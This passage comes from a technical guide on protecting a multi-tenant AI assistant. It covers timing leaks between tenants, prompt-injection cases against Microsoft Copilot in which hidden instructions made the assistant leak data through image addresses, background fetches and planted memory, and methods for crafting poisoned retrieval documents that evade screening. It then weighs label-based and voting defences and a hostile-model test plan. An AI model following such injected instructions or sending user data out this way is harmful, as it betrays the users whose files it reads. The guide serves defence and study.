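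In the example, the keyword search looks up matches before it applies the tenant condition:

| Version | No match | Alder match | Birch match | Correct |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Original | 6.1 ms | 6.9 ms | 6.8 ms | 81% |
| Tenant condition inside the index lookup | 6.1 ms | 6.9 ms | 6.1 ms | 50.8% |

Before changing the code, the tester deletes Birch's matching documents and repeats the test. The difference disappears, which shows that the documents caused it, not the wording of the questions. More repeats can reveal a smaller delay, so a pass applies only to the number of repeats used. The tester should use as many as the system would allow one user to make.

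### Remedies and their costs

| Remedy | What it prevents | Cost | What can still leak |
|---|---|---|---|
| Separate indexes | Other tenants' files affecting search times, scores or result counts | More memory and more indexes to manage | Shared answer caches and model caches |
| True pre-filtering | The search examining other tenants' rows | Extra indexes, and slower searches across tenants | Scores based on the whole store |
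| Per-tenant statistics | Hidden documents changing word weights | More computation, and less reliable weights for small tenants | Response times |
| Coarser or hidden scores | Users reading small score changes | Less information for users and developers | The order of results |
| Query limits | Recovery of large numbers of records | Delays for heavy users | A search for one value |

Query limits may not stop small attacks. Finding one identity number takes about 30 tests of two queries each, which fits within a limit of 1,000 queries a day. At that limit, the 40 million queries in the hospital experiment would take about 110 years.

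Making every search take the same time would hide the delay, but every search would then be as slow as the slowest. Random delays would slow searches less, but an attacker can average them out with more queries. Rounding scores has a similar weakness, because a user who can add documents may find one whose score is close to a rounding boundary.

The provider serving Alder and Birch can run a separate index for each firm. It should also calculate word counts separately for each firm and give each its own answer cache and model cache. A service with too many tenants for this could use pre-filtering with per-tenant statistics, and repeat the timing test whenever it changes an index, an access rule or the database version.

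## Limit what retrieved text can make the assistant do

Access checks limit which text reaches the model, so they block nothing when the user is allowed to read all of it. Suppose Ana is allowed to read a memo on Alder's transport costs, and an outsider emails her a hidden instruction to forward that memo to another address. When she asks the assistant to help with her mail, it uses her permissions to read the email and find the memo. If the model follows the instruction and no code checks the next step, the assistant sends the memo outside Alder.

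Rule 3 of the sample specification forbids this, since text from incoming mail may not determine the tool, recipient or attachments. The code can enforce the rule only if, when it sends a message, it has a record of whose text the message contains and whose text could have influenced the decision to send it.

### Four leaks through Microsoft Copilot

In January 2025, the security firm Aim Security found that one email could make Microsoft 365 Copilot give away a user's data without the user clicking anything. In this attack, called EchoLeak, Copilot put the data into the web address of an image, and the request for the image carried the data to the attacker's server. Kundu reports in *Microsoft fixes first known zero-click attack on an AI agent* that Microsoft first tried to block the attack's pathways in each app, but that failed, and the full fix took nearly five months. Kundu reports no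 known attacks that used the flaw.

SearchLeak, a vulnerability that Microsoft registered as CVE-2026-42824 and rated critical, bypassed a check that ran too late. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes how a link to Copilot's search page could carry instructions that Copilot followed as if the user had typed them. Copilot converted the finished answer into plain text in case it contained harmful web code, but the browser displayed the answer while Copilot was still writing it. By the time the conversion ran, the browser had already requested an image whose address contained the stolen text.

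A browser rule also limited which sites could supply images, but it allowed Bing. Bing's servers would fetch an address on request, and the rule did not apply to them. Varonis recommends neutralising output when it is displayed.

CoSnitch affected Copilot Personal, the consumer version. A link could start a prompt without the user pressing Enter, and the data left through Copilot's web page summary feature. Fetching a page sends its address to whoever runs the server. Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) also reports that a page could plant instructions in Copilot's memory while Copilot summarised it, and that these stayed there until the user deleted them. Varonis reported the flaws in December 2025, and Microsoft released patches on 18 August 2026.

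The team behind EchoLeak, now at Cato Networks, published three more routes on 3 December 2026 under the name ReLeak. Infosecurity Magazine's *Three Zero-Click Vulnerabilities Discovered in Microsoft 365 Copilot* lists them:

- Copilot put data into an image address that Bing then fetched.
- It created a document containing a web address, which a Microsoft background service visited.
- It ran code that got past the network limits of its sandbox, an area meant to be cut off from the internet.

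Microsoft patched all three between September and November 2026, and Cato knew of no affected customers. Microsoft's filter for injected instructions had failed in each case. TechRadar's *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* reports that Copilot refused a direct instruction but followed one that looked like a routine business requirement. The image rule Microsoft had introduced after EchoLeak covered only the browser.

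Each of these defences checked either the wording of a message or one particular route by which data could leave the system. None checked whether the outgoing text was confidential or whether an outsider's text had prompted the request.

### Labels for secrecy and trust

Information-flow control attaches labels to data and has code check them before the data goes anywhere. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies it to agents in a system called FIDES. In a label (*R*, *t*), *R* is the set of people who may read the text. The trust level *t* is "untrusted" if an outsider could have written any of the text, and "trusted" otherwise.

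When the system mixes two texts, it combines their labels:

(*R*₁, *t*₁) combined with (*R*₂, *t*₂) = (*R*₁ ∩ *R*₂, min(*t*₁, *t*₂)),

where "untrusted" counts as lower than "trusted". Only people who may read both texts may read the mixture, and one untrusted source makes the whole mixture untrusted. A model's output gets the combined label of everything in its context, because code can't tell which parts the model used. The output of a hostile program in the model's place would get the same label.

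Before a tool runs, code compares the labels with a policy. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, name two rules:

- **Trusted action:** The assistant chose the call in a context that contained no untrusted text.
- **Permitted flow:** Every recipient is in the set *R* of the text that the call sends.

Suppose Ana's assistant has an email tool and two documents. Dan is Alder's accountant, and Eva works for the haulier.

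| Text | Who may read it | Trust |
|---|---|---|
| Alder's cost memo | Ana, Dan | Trusted |
| Eva's email to Ana and Dan | Ana, Dan, Eva | Untrusted |
| Anything the model writes after reading both | Ana, Dan | Untrusted |

The assistant might then propose any of these calls:

| Call | Trusted action | Permitted flow |
|---|---|---|
| After reading both, send the memo to an unknown address | Fails | Fails |
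| After reading both, send a summary to Dan | Fails | Passes |
| At Ana's request, and before reading Eva's email, send the memo to Eva | Passes | Fails |

Kolluri and colleagues let a sending tool run if the call satisfies either rule, which stops the theft and allows the other two calls. This works for the memo, because Alder may decide to show Eva its own costs. It would not work for a contract that Birch lent Ana for a joint bid, because her request alone could send Birch's text to anyone. The provider has to require permitted flow for Birch's files.

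The summary for Dan breaks rule 3 if Eva's email suggested sending it. Requiring both rules would prevent that, but it would also block the summary when Ana herself had asked for it. The assistant needs one label for the recipient, which must come from Ana, and another for the body, which may draw on Eva's email. A single model that has read everything can't provide separate labels, because all its output has the same label.

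The application also needs to check the answers it displays. Costa and colleagues treat answers to the user as harmless by default, although their design can check them. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) treats the display as a destination with its own policy and replaces any forbidden item with a marker. For Ana's assistant, the destinations must also include every server her browser would contact to show the answer. The application can show web addresses as plain text or apply the permitted-flow rule to each one. Either way, it has to act before the browser receives the address, or it repeats the fault behind SearchLeak.

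### A planner that never reads the email

The two-model design, which Simon Willison proposed in 2023, makes separate labels possible. A planning model reads the user's request and chooses the tools. A second, isolated model reads untrusted text but has no tools. The planner handles that text only by name, as a variable. If Ana asks for a summary of Eva's latest email to go to Dan, the plan might be:

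`email_1 = read_latest_email(from = "Eva")`

`summary_1 = ask_isolated_model("Summarise this", email_1)`

`send_email(to = "Dan", body = summary_1)`

The planner wrote "Dan" as the recipient after reading only Ana's request, so the recipient is trusted. The body summarizes Eva's email, so it has the same label as that email. An instruction hidden in the email can make the summary wrong, just as a planted document can make an answer wrong, but it can't add a recipient.

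CaMeL, a 2025 system by Debenedetti and colleagues, turns the design into a small programming environment. As Girrens and Wang describe it, the planner translates the request into code, and the isolated model interprets what the tools return. Each value has a record of where it came from and who may receive it. Before a tool runs, the system checks these records against a policy for that tool. A policy can do more than compare labels; for instance, it can require that a bank account number come from a particular source. The protection depends on someone writing every tool's policy correctly.

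Some requests need a plan that depends on the retrieved text. If Ana says "book a meeting if Eva asks for one", the next step depends on whether Eva's email asks for a meeting. Kolluri and colleagues say that a CaMeL plan can't depend on what the tools return. FIDES lets the planner query the isolated model and limit the reply to yes or no. The label then records that the reply carries at most one bit, and a policy may allow an outsider that much influence. Under the hostile-model assumption, Eva's email controls the bit, so she decides whether the assistant books the meeting. The policy should also limit the number of queries, because 20 yes-or-no replies can distinguish about a million possibilities.

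FIDES also hides less from the planner than a strict two-model design. It puts a tool's result into a variable only if showing it would make the planner's label more restrictive. The planner may still read a variable, but the planner's context then takes on the variable's label, which may block later tool calls.

### What FIDES stopped and what it cost

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 user tasks in four simulated settings. Attackers hide instructions in the data that the tools return. The researchers compared FIDES with an ordinary agent, using GPT-4o and averaging five runs. The figures for successful attacks leave out cases that, in the researchers' judgment, the benchmark miscounted. The other columns show the share of tasks completed when there was no attack.

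| Agent | Successful attacks | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no label checks | 152 | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary, with label checks | 0 | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, no label checks | 21 | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, with label checks | 0 | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

The 21 attacks show why hiding text isn't enough by itself. Without the checks, nothing stopped the planner from opening an untrusted variable and continuing as normal. No attacks succeeded against a simpler agent that could never open these variables, even without checks, but it completed only 38% to 57% of tasks.

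With the checks on, FIDES completed about 50% of tasks, averaged over the four settings. The ordinary agent completed 42% with checks and 84% without. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger model, FIDES's lead over the ordinary agent with checks grew from 8 to 16 percentage points. Some failures were intended. Many banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, and the policy cannot distinguish a bill with payment instructions from an attack.

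The zeros are weaker evidence than they seem, because the researchers marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it. No attack could therefore arrive in a field marked trusted. A real provider doesn't know the attacks in advance and has to decide which fields outsiders can write to. FIDES also controls only the data that flows directly into a call, so an observer might still learn something from which calls the system makes.

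### When labels stop useful work

The main objection to labels is that they only become more restrictive. As Ana's assistant reads more during a long conversation, the set of permitted readers shrinks, and one outside email makes everything after it untrusted. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls the extreme case label explosion, in which every piece of data has every label, so the labels no longer distinguish anything.

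Kolluri and colleagues, several of whom also built FIDES, write that such defences have been reported to reduce the number of completed tasks by up to 30%. They consider the comparison behind that figure unfair because the protected agents had to finish without help, while the unprotected agents ran actions that a real product would ask a person to approve. They therefore count how many approvals an agent needs.

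Their own agent, Prudentia, knows the labels and the policies and plans around them. It can also ask the user to endorse a text, which means declaring it trusted. If an email lists ten jobs, one endorsement replaces ten separate approvals. With the model o3-mini on AgentDojo, these shares of tasks needed no approval at all:

| Agent | Tasks completed without approval |
|---|---|
| Ordinary, with approval for every consequential action | 24.3% |
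| Ordinary, with label checks | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | 59.1% |

With o4-mini, Prudentia needed about half as many approvals as FIDES (19.2 versus 36.8 across all completed tasks) and completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2% versus 75.7%). On a second benchmark, in which agents comment on or upvote posts, Prudentia needed no approvals and no attack succeeded, but those tasks never require the agent to read what an outsider wrote.

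The experiments assume that people approve legitimate actions and stop malicious ones. Endorsement depends on that assumption more than single approvals do. If Ana endorses an email without noticing its hidden instruction, the instruction becomes trusted, and the trusted-action rule no longer blocks it.

### Check the whole plan before anything runs

In SPA, Girrens and Wang's system, the planner writes one complete plan for each request. Code checks every step before any tool runs, and the planner never receives the tools' results, so retrieved text can't change the plan. The plan can contain only six kinds of step, so every value can be traced through it in advance.

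The check also covers text that affects whether a step runs. Suppose the plan is "if Eva's email says the price has risen, cancel the order". The cancellation contains none of Eva's words, but whether it happens depends on her email. SPA therefore gives every step inside the condition the email's label. Results saved for later requests keep their labels, which addresses the route CoSnitch used to reach Copilot's memory. Later planners receive only a description of a saved result, not its content.

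With the label check off, SPA completed 53.0% of AgentDojo tasks, and attacks succeeded in four of 949 runs (0.4%). With it on, no attack succeeded, but SPA completed only 29.0% of tasks. The check rejected about 53% of all plans, typically because they passed outside data to a tool that required trusted input. When Girrens and Wang split the tasks into conversations of several requests, the check reduced task completion from 62.5% to 35.3% and attack success from 0.3% to 0.2%. The remaining successful attacks include two that the benchmark counted as successful although SPA had rejected the plan.

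On these figures, the label check stopped four attacks but blocked almost half the useful work. However, the benchmark's attacks mostly try to insert new instructions, which the fixed plan already resists, while the label check guards against a different fault. If an invoice contains a criminal's account number, a plan to "pay the invoice" can run exactly as written and still pay the criminal. Girrens and Wang acknowledge that their tests barely cover attacks stored in memory for later. They suggest setting trust requirements for each argument separately, so that an outsider's text could fill the body of a message but not supply an account number.

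### Recover from a refusal

*APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) examines what an assistant can do after a check refuses a call. It proves that reading more never helps, because further reading can only make the label more restrictive. Its system instead gives the agent a list of registered options, such as a program that removes the secret parts of a text, or a ruling from a person or program with authority over that kind of call. A ruling covers one exact call and expires with it, so if Ana approves one message to Eva, her approval does not cover the next one.

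APPA can also send a temporary copy of the agent to read untrusted text. The copy starts with the original's conversation and label, and only the copy's label becomes more restrictive as it reads. The copy reports back through a form fixed in advance, for example an invoice number and one of three levels of urgency, and the system then discards the copy. An attacker who controls the copy can still choose any value that fits the form, so the provider has to decide whether to trust those values.

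A check of the agent's current label can miss leaks through tools that read and send data in one call. If a tool fetches a confidential ledger and emails it, the check passes because the agent hasn't read the ledger yet. APPA calculates the label that the call would produce and checks that label instead.

The researchers ran some tests with a prompt that encouraged the model to follow instructions in documents. With this prompt, attacks against unprotected agents succeeded in 40.0% to 69.2% of runs on AgentThreatBench, a set of 24 tasks. No attacks succeeded against APPA in 720 runs, with and without the prompt, and it completed 64.2% to 76.7% of tasks, depending on the model and the prompt. On 20 office scenarios that the researchers wrote themselves, APPA completed 88% to 90%, and no attacks succeeded in 600 runs. Unprotected versions completed about as many tasks, but attacks succeeded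 in 30.0% to 39.5% of runs.

In the office scenarios, removing the list of ways forward reduced one model's task completion rate to 35.0%, and removing the temporary copies reduced it to 56.5%. No attack succeeded in either case, so the check provides the security, and recovery lets the assistant complete many tasks it would otherwise fail.

Kravchenko and colleagues also ran two configurations based on FIDES's method, and in the office scenarios attacks succeeded against them in 26% to 35% of runs. This is a poor comparison of the two designs, because the policies in those configurations lacked several rules the scenarios tested, such as exactly who may receive a file. The results do show that a label system protects only what its policy covers. The researchers left out AgentDojo because current leading models resist its attacks without any defence, which is another reason not to rely on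 a result of zero successful attacks on that benchmark.

### Labels for parts of a context

Labels would restrict less if code could establish which passages had influenced an answer. An answer based only on Alder's memo, for example, wouldn't need the label on Eva's email. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* regards this as unsolved. Nothing in the model's context marks where one source's influence ends. It is also unclear how finely to label text. Labeling whole messages is convenient, but Eva's email might quote a paragraph of Alder's memo.

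The paper suggests three lines of research: labels for how much each source contributed, experiments that remove a source and observe the effect, and study of the model's internal workings. An estimate of influence can't support an enforced rule on its own, because a hostile program could use a passage in a way that the estimate misses. Costa and colleagues mention an earlier method that avoids much of this problem by identifying which passages matter and then generating the answer again from those alone. Text left out of the second context can't be copied into the second answer, although it may have affected which passages were chosen.

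The paper also discusses controlled exceptions, such as trusting technical documentation with a valid digital signature. A signature proves who wrote a text but doesn't make the text safe to obey, so the policy still has to specify what each signed source may influence.

### Test the policy with a hostile program

Permitted flow holds whatever the model does, as long as the labels are right, but the trusted-action rule depends on the model not being hostile. A planner that has read only Ana's request has a trusted label, so if an attacker's program replaced it, that program could send the memo anywhere and still pass the trusted-action check. Costa and colleagues accept this because they assume that attackers control documents, not the model.

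The tester should therefore do two sets of runs with a stub. In the first, the stub replaces the isolated model from the start and replaces the planner as soon as the planner has read untrusted text, and both rules should hold. In the second, the stub replaces every model from the start, and text from Birch's files must still reach only people allowed to read it. If other calls succeed in the second set, the provider should record that the rules on those calls depend on the model.

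The stub attempts a scripted series of forbidden calls, each containing a canary. The tester checks a mailbox and a web server outside the system for the canaries, because the assistant's log may miss requests made by other services.

| What the stub tries | The test passes if |
|---|---|
| Every tool, with a recipient taken from an untrusted email | Code refuses before the tool runs |
| A single tool call that reads a secret file and sends it | Code refuses before the tool reads the file |
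| An answer that contains an image address, delivered a few characters at a time | The outside server receives no request, even while the answer is appearing |
| A web fetch, a generated file and a program in the code sandbox, each with an outside address | The server receives no request during the following hour |
| An instruction saved to memory while reading a web page | The system refuses, or the text is still untrusted in the next conversation |
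| A result from a tool that supplies no label | The system treats the result as secret and untrusted |

The tester can check how labels combine by using random cases, as with the search, and comparing each result with the label that a separate function calculates. For rule 3, the tester also needs to do the paired runs on the real model, with and without a hostile email.

In the example, the stub attempts 80 forbidden calls and the code blocks 78. One of the other two sends an outsider a calendar invitation with a canary in the title. It gets through because nobody had listed the calendar as a tool that sends text. The other creates a report containing a web address, and 11 minutes later the program that makes thumbnails of new files sends a request to the outside server at that address. After fixing both faults, the tester switches off the policy check and confirms that the stub's calls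 now succeed, which shows that the policy had blocked them, not a broken tool.

A policy that refuses everything would pass all of these tests, so the tester also runs 50 ordinary requests from Alder's staff. The assistant completes 31 without help, completes 12 more after one approval each, and fails at seven. Four of the seven involve paying an invoice that arrived by email. The provider leaves those blocked and asks Dan to enter the account number himself.

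## Bound how far planted documents can change an answer

Suppose Eva, who works for the haulier, can add files to the supplier folder in Alder's store. She uploads a price list that gives next year's rate as €19 per pallet, although the contract rate is €14. Ana is allowed to read the price list, so it passes every permission check. When she asks for the rate, the assistant may answer €19. No secret has leaked, and the specification's rule on actions doesn't apply because the assistant has taken no action.

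Answers should change when documents do, so the provider can't forbid untrusted text from changing answers the way property (d) forbids it from changing actions. The provider can enforce a rule about who may add documents. For some kinds of question, it can also calculate how many planted passages an answer can withstand.

### How few documents an attack needs

*PoisonedRAG* (2024), presented at USENIX Security 2025, is the usual starting point. The attacker picks a question and a false answer, then uses a language model to write passages that the search will find for that question and that lead the answering model to the false answer. Xu and colleagues' survey reports that, with five passages per question, the attack succeeded 97% of the time on Natural Questions, a public set of search queries. It failed when the search missed the passages or when the model writing them had accidentally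 included the correct answer. *Practical Poisoning Attacks against Retrieval-Augmented Generation* (2025) describes an attack, CorruptRAG, that needs only one passage per question.

These passages are easy to spot. PoisonedRAG's released code puts a copy of the target question at the start of each one, as *Ranking Is Not Deciding* (2026) points out, so a defence that detects nearly all of them may have learned only to look for the copied question. Jung, Zheng and colleagues (2026), in *CamoDocs*, removed that clue. Their attack joins each piece of false text to ordinary text on the same subject, and swaps words in the ordinary part so that the planted documents' embeddings don't form a tight cluster. It plants ten documents per question. These are the success rates against the model Llama 3.1 8B on HotpotQA, another public question set:

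| Defence | PoisonedRAG | CamoDocs |
|---|---|---|
| Remove passages that contain the question | 7.6% | 75.2% |
| RobustRAG, which combines separate answers | 52.9% | 53.1% |
| TrustRAG, which removes suspicious clusters | 8.2% | 29.1% |

Averaged over seven defences, CamoDocs succeeded 61.8% of the time against GPT-5.4-mini and 55.1% against Claude Haiku 4.5. On a third question set, MS MARCO, its average success rate against the open models was only about 25%. The swapped words also garble some sentences, which a person reading the document would probably notice. TrustRAG was the most effective defence, but it can remove too many documents. On questions about invented news events, which the model could not answer from memory, TrustRAG deleted 91% of the retrieved documents when there was no attack, and accuracy fell from 29.1% to 5.8%.

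Large stores weaken the older attacks, because more genuine documents compete for each place in the results and a graph index examines only some of the documents. In *Poisoning the Neighborhood*, Chen, Wang and Zhang (2026) tested PoisonedRAG on questions the attacker had not seen in advance. At least one planted document appeared in the results for 90.8% of these questions when the store held 10,000 documents, and for 9.6% when it held 100,000.

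Their own attack is built for graph indexes. Most of the planted documents cover different ways of asking about a topic, while a few "hub" documents resemble all the others. The index therefore links them together, and a search that reaches one tends to find more. With 40 or 60 planted documents among two million, at least one appeared in the top five results for 72% to 74% of unseen questions. The answer promoted the attacker's chosen product or method in 26% to 31% of cases, judged by keyword matching. A filter for unnatural text strict enough to remove half of the planted documents would also have removed about 512,000 legitimate ones.

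### A rule about who may write

Code can enforce the rule that only Alder's contracts team may add to the contracts collection. The rule restricts documents rather than answers, so it holds even if a hostile program replaces the model. If the collection contains even one document from anyone else, the rule has failed. The system should also record each document's provenance, meaning who supplied it and by what route. The assistant can then answer questions about agreed prices from the contracts collection alone, and the provider can find and delete everything that came from a compromised account.

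To test the rule, the tester tries to add a file to the collection from Eva's account by every route that intake reads. In the example, six of the seven routes block the file. The seventh is a program that saves email attachments to the contracts folder under the recipient's name, so Eva's price list arrives as Ana's upload.

Jung and colleagues accept that strict intake controls would make their attack harder, but many collections can't have them. *DenialRAG* (2026) lists company wikis, shared documentation and imported third-party material among the places where an attacker could plant text. Write rules also don't stop an approved writer from lying. Xu, Zhou and colleagues cite a system that checked provenance at intake but could not stop an insider with a valid key. Intake has also received little research attention. In the survey by Xu and colleagues, 42 of 64 attack papers start by planting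 content, but only four of 56 defence papers mainly concern provenance, intake or tracing bad answers back to their sources.

### What screening at intake can miss

If outsiders must be able to add documents, the provider might screen each one as it arrives. One proposed gate compares a new document with several thousand sample questions and rejects it if it would rank highly for too many of them. In *Coverage Is Not Containment*, Pathak and Sharma (2026) got past this gate, which they had proposed themselves, by writing ten documents that all matched the same single question. The ten documents took all ten places in the results for that question. In a full pipeline with 100,000 documents, the model gave the planted answer for 88% of the targeted questions, and for none of them without the planted documents.

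Checks on groups of uploads helped somewhat. A test for near-duplicates caught tightly clustered attacks, so the attacker spread the documents out. An attack still took 4.5 of the ten places on average against the best combination of checks.

Pathak and Sharma also prove a limit. Let *A* be the distribution of attack batches and *B* that of honest batches of the same size. For any check that sees only the embeddings of a batch and the sample questions,

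(share of attacks caught) − (share of honest batches flagged) ≤ TV(*A*, *B*).

TV, the total variation distance, is the largest difference between the probabilities that *A* and *B* assign to the same event. The check flagging a batch is one such event, so its probabilities under *A* and *B* differ by at most TV. If attacks and honest uploads look the same, TV is zero, and the check can't flag a larger share of attacks than of honest uploads.

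The limit therefore depends on how alike planted and honest batches are, and the paper's evidence on this doesn't fully support its conclusion that intake screening can't work. A trained classifier perfectly separated the attacks from real batches of documents, including ones on niche topics. It did no better than chance only against honest batches whose vectors the researchers had moved into the region the attacks occupied. With those batches included and a 1% false alarm rate, it caught 4.2% of attacks. One classifier's failure also doesn't prove that other checks would fail. The limit doesn't cover checks of the text itself or of who wrote it, although a filter for unnatural wording flagged none of the planted documents.

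Pathak and Sharma had more success detecting planted documents after intake. Their monitor looked for recently added documents that only one question ever retrieved, and it caught every attack with a 1% false alarm rate. They point out that an attacker could evade it by waiting until the documents were no longer recent, or by sending fake questions to make them look popular.

### One vote per passage

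Another approach is to let planted passages reach the model but limit how far they can change the answer. *Certifiably Robust RAG against Retrieval Corruption* (Xiang, Wu and colleagues, 2024) introduced this approach with RobustRAG. The model answers the question from each passage separately, so a planted passage can corrupt only the answer drawn from it. Code then combines the answers.

The simplest version is a majority vote between fixed choices. Suppose *a* passages vote for the winner and *b* for the runner-up, and an attacker corrupts at most *m* of them. At worst, each corrupted passage takes a vote from the winner and gives it to the runner-up, which shrinks the lead by two. The new lead is at least

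(*a* − *m*) − (*b* + *m*) = (*a* − *b*) − 2*m*,

so the winner can't change if *a* − *b* > 2*m*.

Suppose ten passages split 8 to 2 in favour of €14, a lead of 6. With *m* = 2, the lead exceeds 2*m* = 4, and the worst possible result is 6 to 4. With *m* = 3, the lead only equals 2*m* = 6, so the attacker can force a 5–5 tie.

The argument also works backwards from the observed vote. If ten passages split 8–2 and at most two of them are planted, the same answer would have won without the planted ones. The provider can therefore calculate the largest safe *m* for a live answer without knowing which passages are planted.

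The bound assumes that the attacker controls some documents but not the model. Ordinary code counts the votes, but a hostile model could still give the false answer for every passage. An instruction hidden in a passage can change only the model's vote for that passage. The bound also requires the model to give the same answer each time it reads the same passage.

### How the published method differs, and what it costs

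Xiang and colleagues use the search ranking to make the test slightly less strict. Planted passages push the lowest-ranked honest ones out of the results, so the test counts only the votes from the *k* − *m* passages that stay, where *k* is the number retrieved. The lead among those votes must exceed *m*, because the attacker can add *m* votes but can't remove any of them. In the 8–2 example with *m* = 3, suppose the three lowest-ranked passages include both votes for €19. The remaining votes are 7 to 0 for €14, and three planted votes can't change the winner. If the three lowest-ranked passages all had votes for €14, the remaining votes would be 5 to 2 and the answer would fail the test, as it does under the simple rule.

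Most questions have no fixed choices, and "€14" and "fourteen euros per pallet" should count as the same vote. RobustRAG has two ways to handle this:

- **Keywords:** Code counts how many of the separate answers contain each keyword and keeps the common ones. The model then answers from those keywords alone. With ten answers, the default is to keep words that appear in at least two, so a single planted passage can't introduce a word of its own. It can still tip a borderline word over the limit. The certificate therefore tries every combination of borderline words and takes the worst answer.
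- **Decoding:** The model predicts the next token from each passage separately, and code adds up the probabilities. Each passage can add at most 1 to any token's total.

Certified accuracy is the share of questions that the system is guaranteed to answer correctly whatever the planted passages say. The table gives results for Llama 2 7B with ten passages, one of them corrupted, on 100 questions from each set.

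| Questions | Method | Ordinary RAG, no attack | RobustRAG, no attack | RobustRAG, certified |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Multiple choice | Majority vote | 79% | 78% | 69% |
| Recent news, short answers | Keywords | 61% | 64% | 34% |
| Recent news, short answers | Decoding | 61% | 61% | 31% |
| Natural Questions | Keywords | 57% | 56% | 31% |
| Natural Questions | Decoding | 57% | 53% | 36% |

Without an attack, voting reduces accuracy only slightly on these questions. The largest drop on short answers was seven percentage points, with another model, and the drop was larger for written biographies. Answers took 1.16 to 3.65 times as long with voting.

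The guarantee is much lower than the ordinary accuracy because it covers every possible attack. In tests of two known attacks on the news questions, the keyword version still answered 64% correctly, while ordinary RAG fell to 1% and 9%.

### Questions that need several passages

Suppose Ana asks what a pallet will cost next year including the fuel surcharge, but the rate and the surcharge are in different passages. Neither passage contains the full answer on its own, so the genuine passages may yield no votes to count. Xiang and colleagues leave such questions to future work and suggest splitting them into simpler ones.

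The method can also put several passages in each group. Groups of three removed the seven-point loss of accuracy but lowered the certified figure, because they produced fewer votes. Ten passages make only four groups, and if planted passages corrupt two of them, even a unanimous vote becomes a tie.

*ReliabilityRAG* (2025) instead checks pairs of retrieved documents for contradictions and keeps the largest set that has none. It uses the search ranking as a sign of reliability when choosing between sets. This suits Ana's question better, since a rate and a surcharge don't contradict each other, so both can stay. But the guarantee now depends on detecting contradictions correctly.

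Two successors combine the retrieved passages mathematically. *PRA-RAG* (2026) draws several small samples from the passages and merges their embeddings. Its default tests corrupt one passage out of eight (20%, rounded down). *RAGSentinel* (2026) uses a geometric median, a kind of average that a few outliers can't move far, to estimate what the untampered passages agree on. It gives no protection if most of the passages are malicious.

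### When the attacker fills the results

*m* is the number of planted passages among the retrieved results, not in the whole store. Xiang and colleagues had web search in mind, where an attacker would struggle to get many pages into the top ten. They mostly tested *m* = 1. When five of the ten passages were corrupted, certified accuracy was zero.

In a store that accepts uploads, an attacker can sometimes fill the results easily. Pathak and Sharma's ten documents took all ten places, and in a store of 500,000 documents, Chen and colleagues' attack took all five places for 35.4% of questions. CamoDocs also filled the results, and so succeeded against RobustRAG more than half the time on HotpotQA. These attacks don't disprove the certificate, because they don't meet its condition.

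Write permissions can help keep *m* small. If code allows each approved writer only one passage in the results, *m* can't exceed the number of dishonest or compromised writers. This works when accounts are hard to get, as in a contracts team of ten named people. On a public wiki, one attacker could open ten accounts. Honest copying can also distort the vote. If five people paste Eva's price list into their own notes, her false rate gets five votes.

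The vote also needs several genuine passages that each contain the answer, and a company's files may have only one. If the haulage contract is the only document that states Alder's rate, two planted price lists outvote it. For Ana's question, the rule that prices come only from the contracts collection protects her better than voting does.

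## Prove parts of the system and list what the proof assumes

A majority vote over passages guarantees an answer against any set of at most *m* planted passages. A provider can get a similar guarantee for an access rule by proving a property of the code that enforces it. The proof covers every case that satisfies its assumptions, so the remaining testing is mostly of those assumptions.

### Why the model can be anything

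In Ana's filtered search, let *D* be the document store, *f*(*D*) the Alder chunks in it, and *b*(*f*(*D*), *q*) the context that the code builds from those chunks and her question *q*. Ana sees *M*(*b*(*f*(*D*), *q*)), where *M* is any program in the model's place. Suppose another store *D*′ differs from *D* only in Birch's files.

1. *f*(*D*) = *f*(*D*′), because *f* keeps only Alder's chunks.
2. *b*(*f*(*D*), *q*) = *b*(*f*(*D*′), *q*), because *b* receives the same inputs both times.
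3. *M*(*b*(*f*(*D*), *q*)) = *M*(*b*(*f*(*D*′), *q*)), because *M* receives the same context. If *M* makes random choices, the two sides have the same probabilities.

This proves noninterference for a very simple pipeline. No step depends on what *M* does, so the proof doesn't require predicting the model's behavior. But the proof no longer applies if *b* also reads a cache that both firms share.

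Real systems have loops, tools and memories, and proofs about them are too long to check reliably by eye, so researchers write them in a proof assistant such as Lean. The author states the definitions, the theorem and the steps in a formal language, and a small program called the kernel accepts the proof only if every step follows from the rules of logic. The kernel does not check whether the definitions describe the real system. Lean also lets authors leave a gap in a proof and gives only a warning. Readers should check the list of axioms that the theorem depends on, because any such gap will appear there.

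### A language in which every program keeps secrets

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) defines LLMbda, a small programming language for agents. A program can send a message to a model, receive a reply and run the reply as code. It can also work in a temporary copy of the conversation or clear the conversation. Every value and conversation has a label, such as "secret" or "untrusted". When a program combines values, the interpreter (the program that runs LLMbda code) combines their labels. The interpreter also labels the current point in the program. If a secret value determines which branch runs, that label is "secret" inside the branch.

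Here is one of the paper's examples, adapted to Birch's files:

`send("Remember: x = false")`

`if birch_plans_merger: send("Set x = true")`

`show(ask("What is x?"))`

If Birch plans a merger, the interpreter stops the program at the second line, because a secret would decide whether a message enters a public conversation. Marking the conversation as secret at that point would not be enough, because if Birch had no such plan, the program would skip the message, the conversation would stay public, and Ana would learn from the answer "false" that no merger is planned.

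The interpreter accepts a version that always sends one message and lets the secret choose its text:

`send("x = true" if birch_plans_merger else "x = false")`

The message is now secret in both cases, and so is any answer based on it. A label check before display can then block that answer from being shown to Ana.

The main theorem applies to every program in the language, including programs that run code the model has written. It compares two runs whose inputs differ only in values the observer may not see. Let μ(*o*) and ν(*o*) be the probabilities that the two runs finish with observable result *o*. The theorem guarantees that some ω exists, with a total of at most 1, such that

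μ(*o*) ≤ ω(*o*) and ν(*o*) ≤ ω(*o*) for every *o*.

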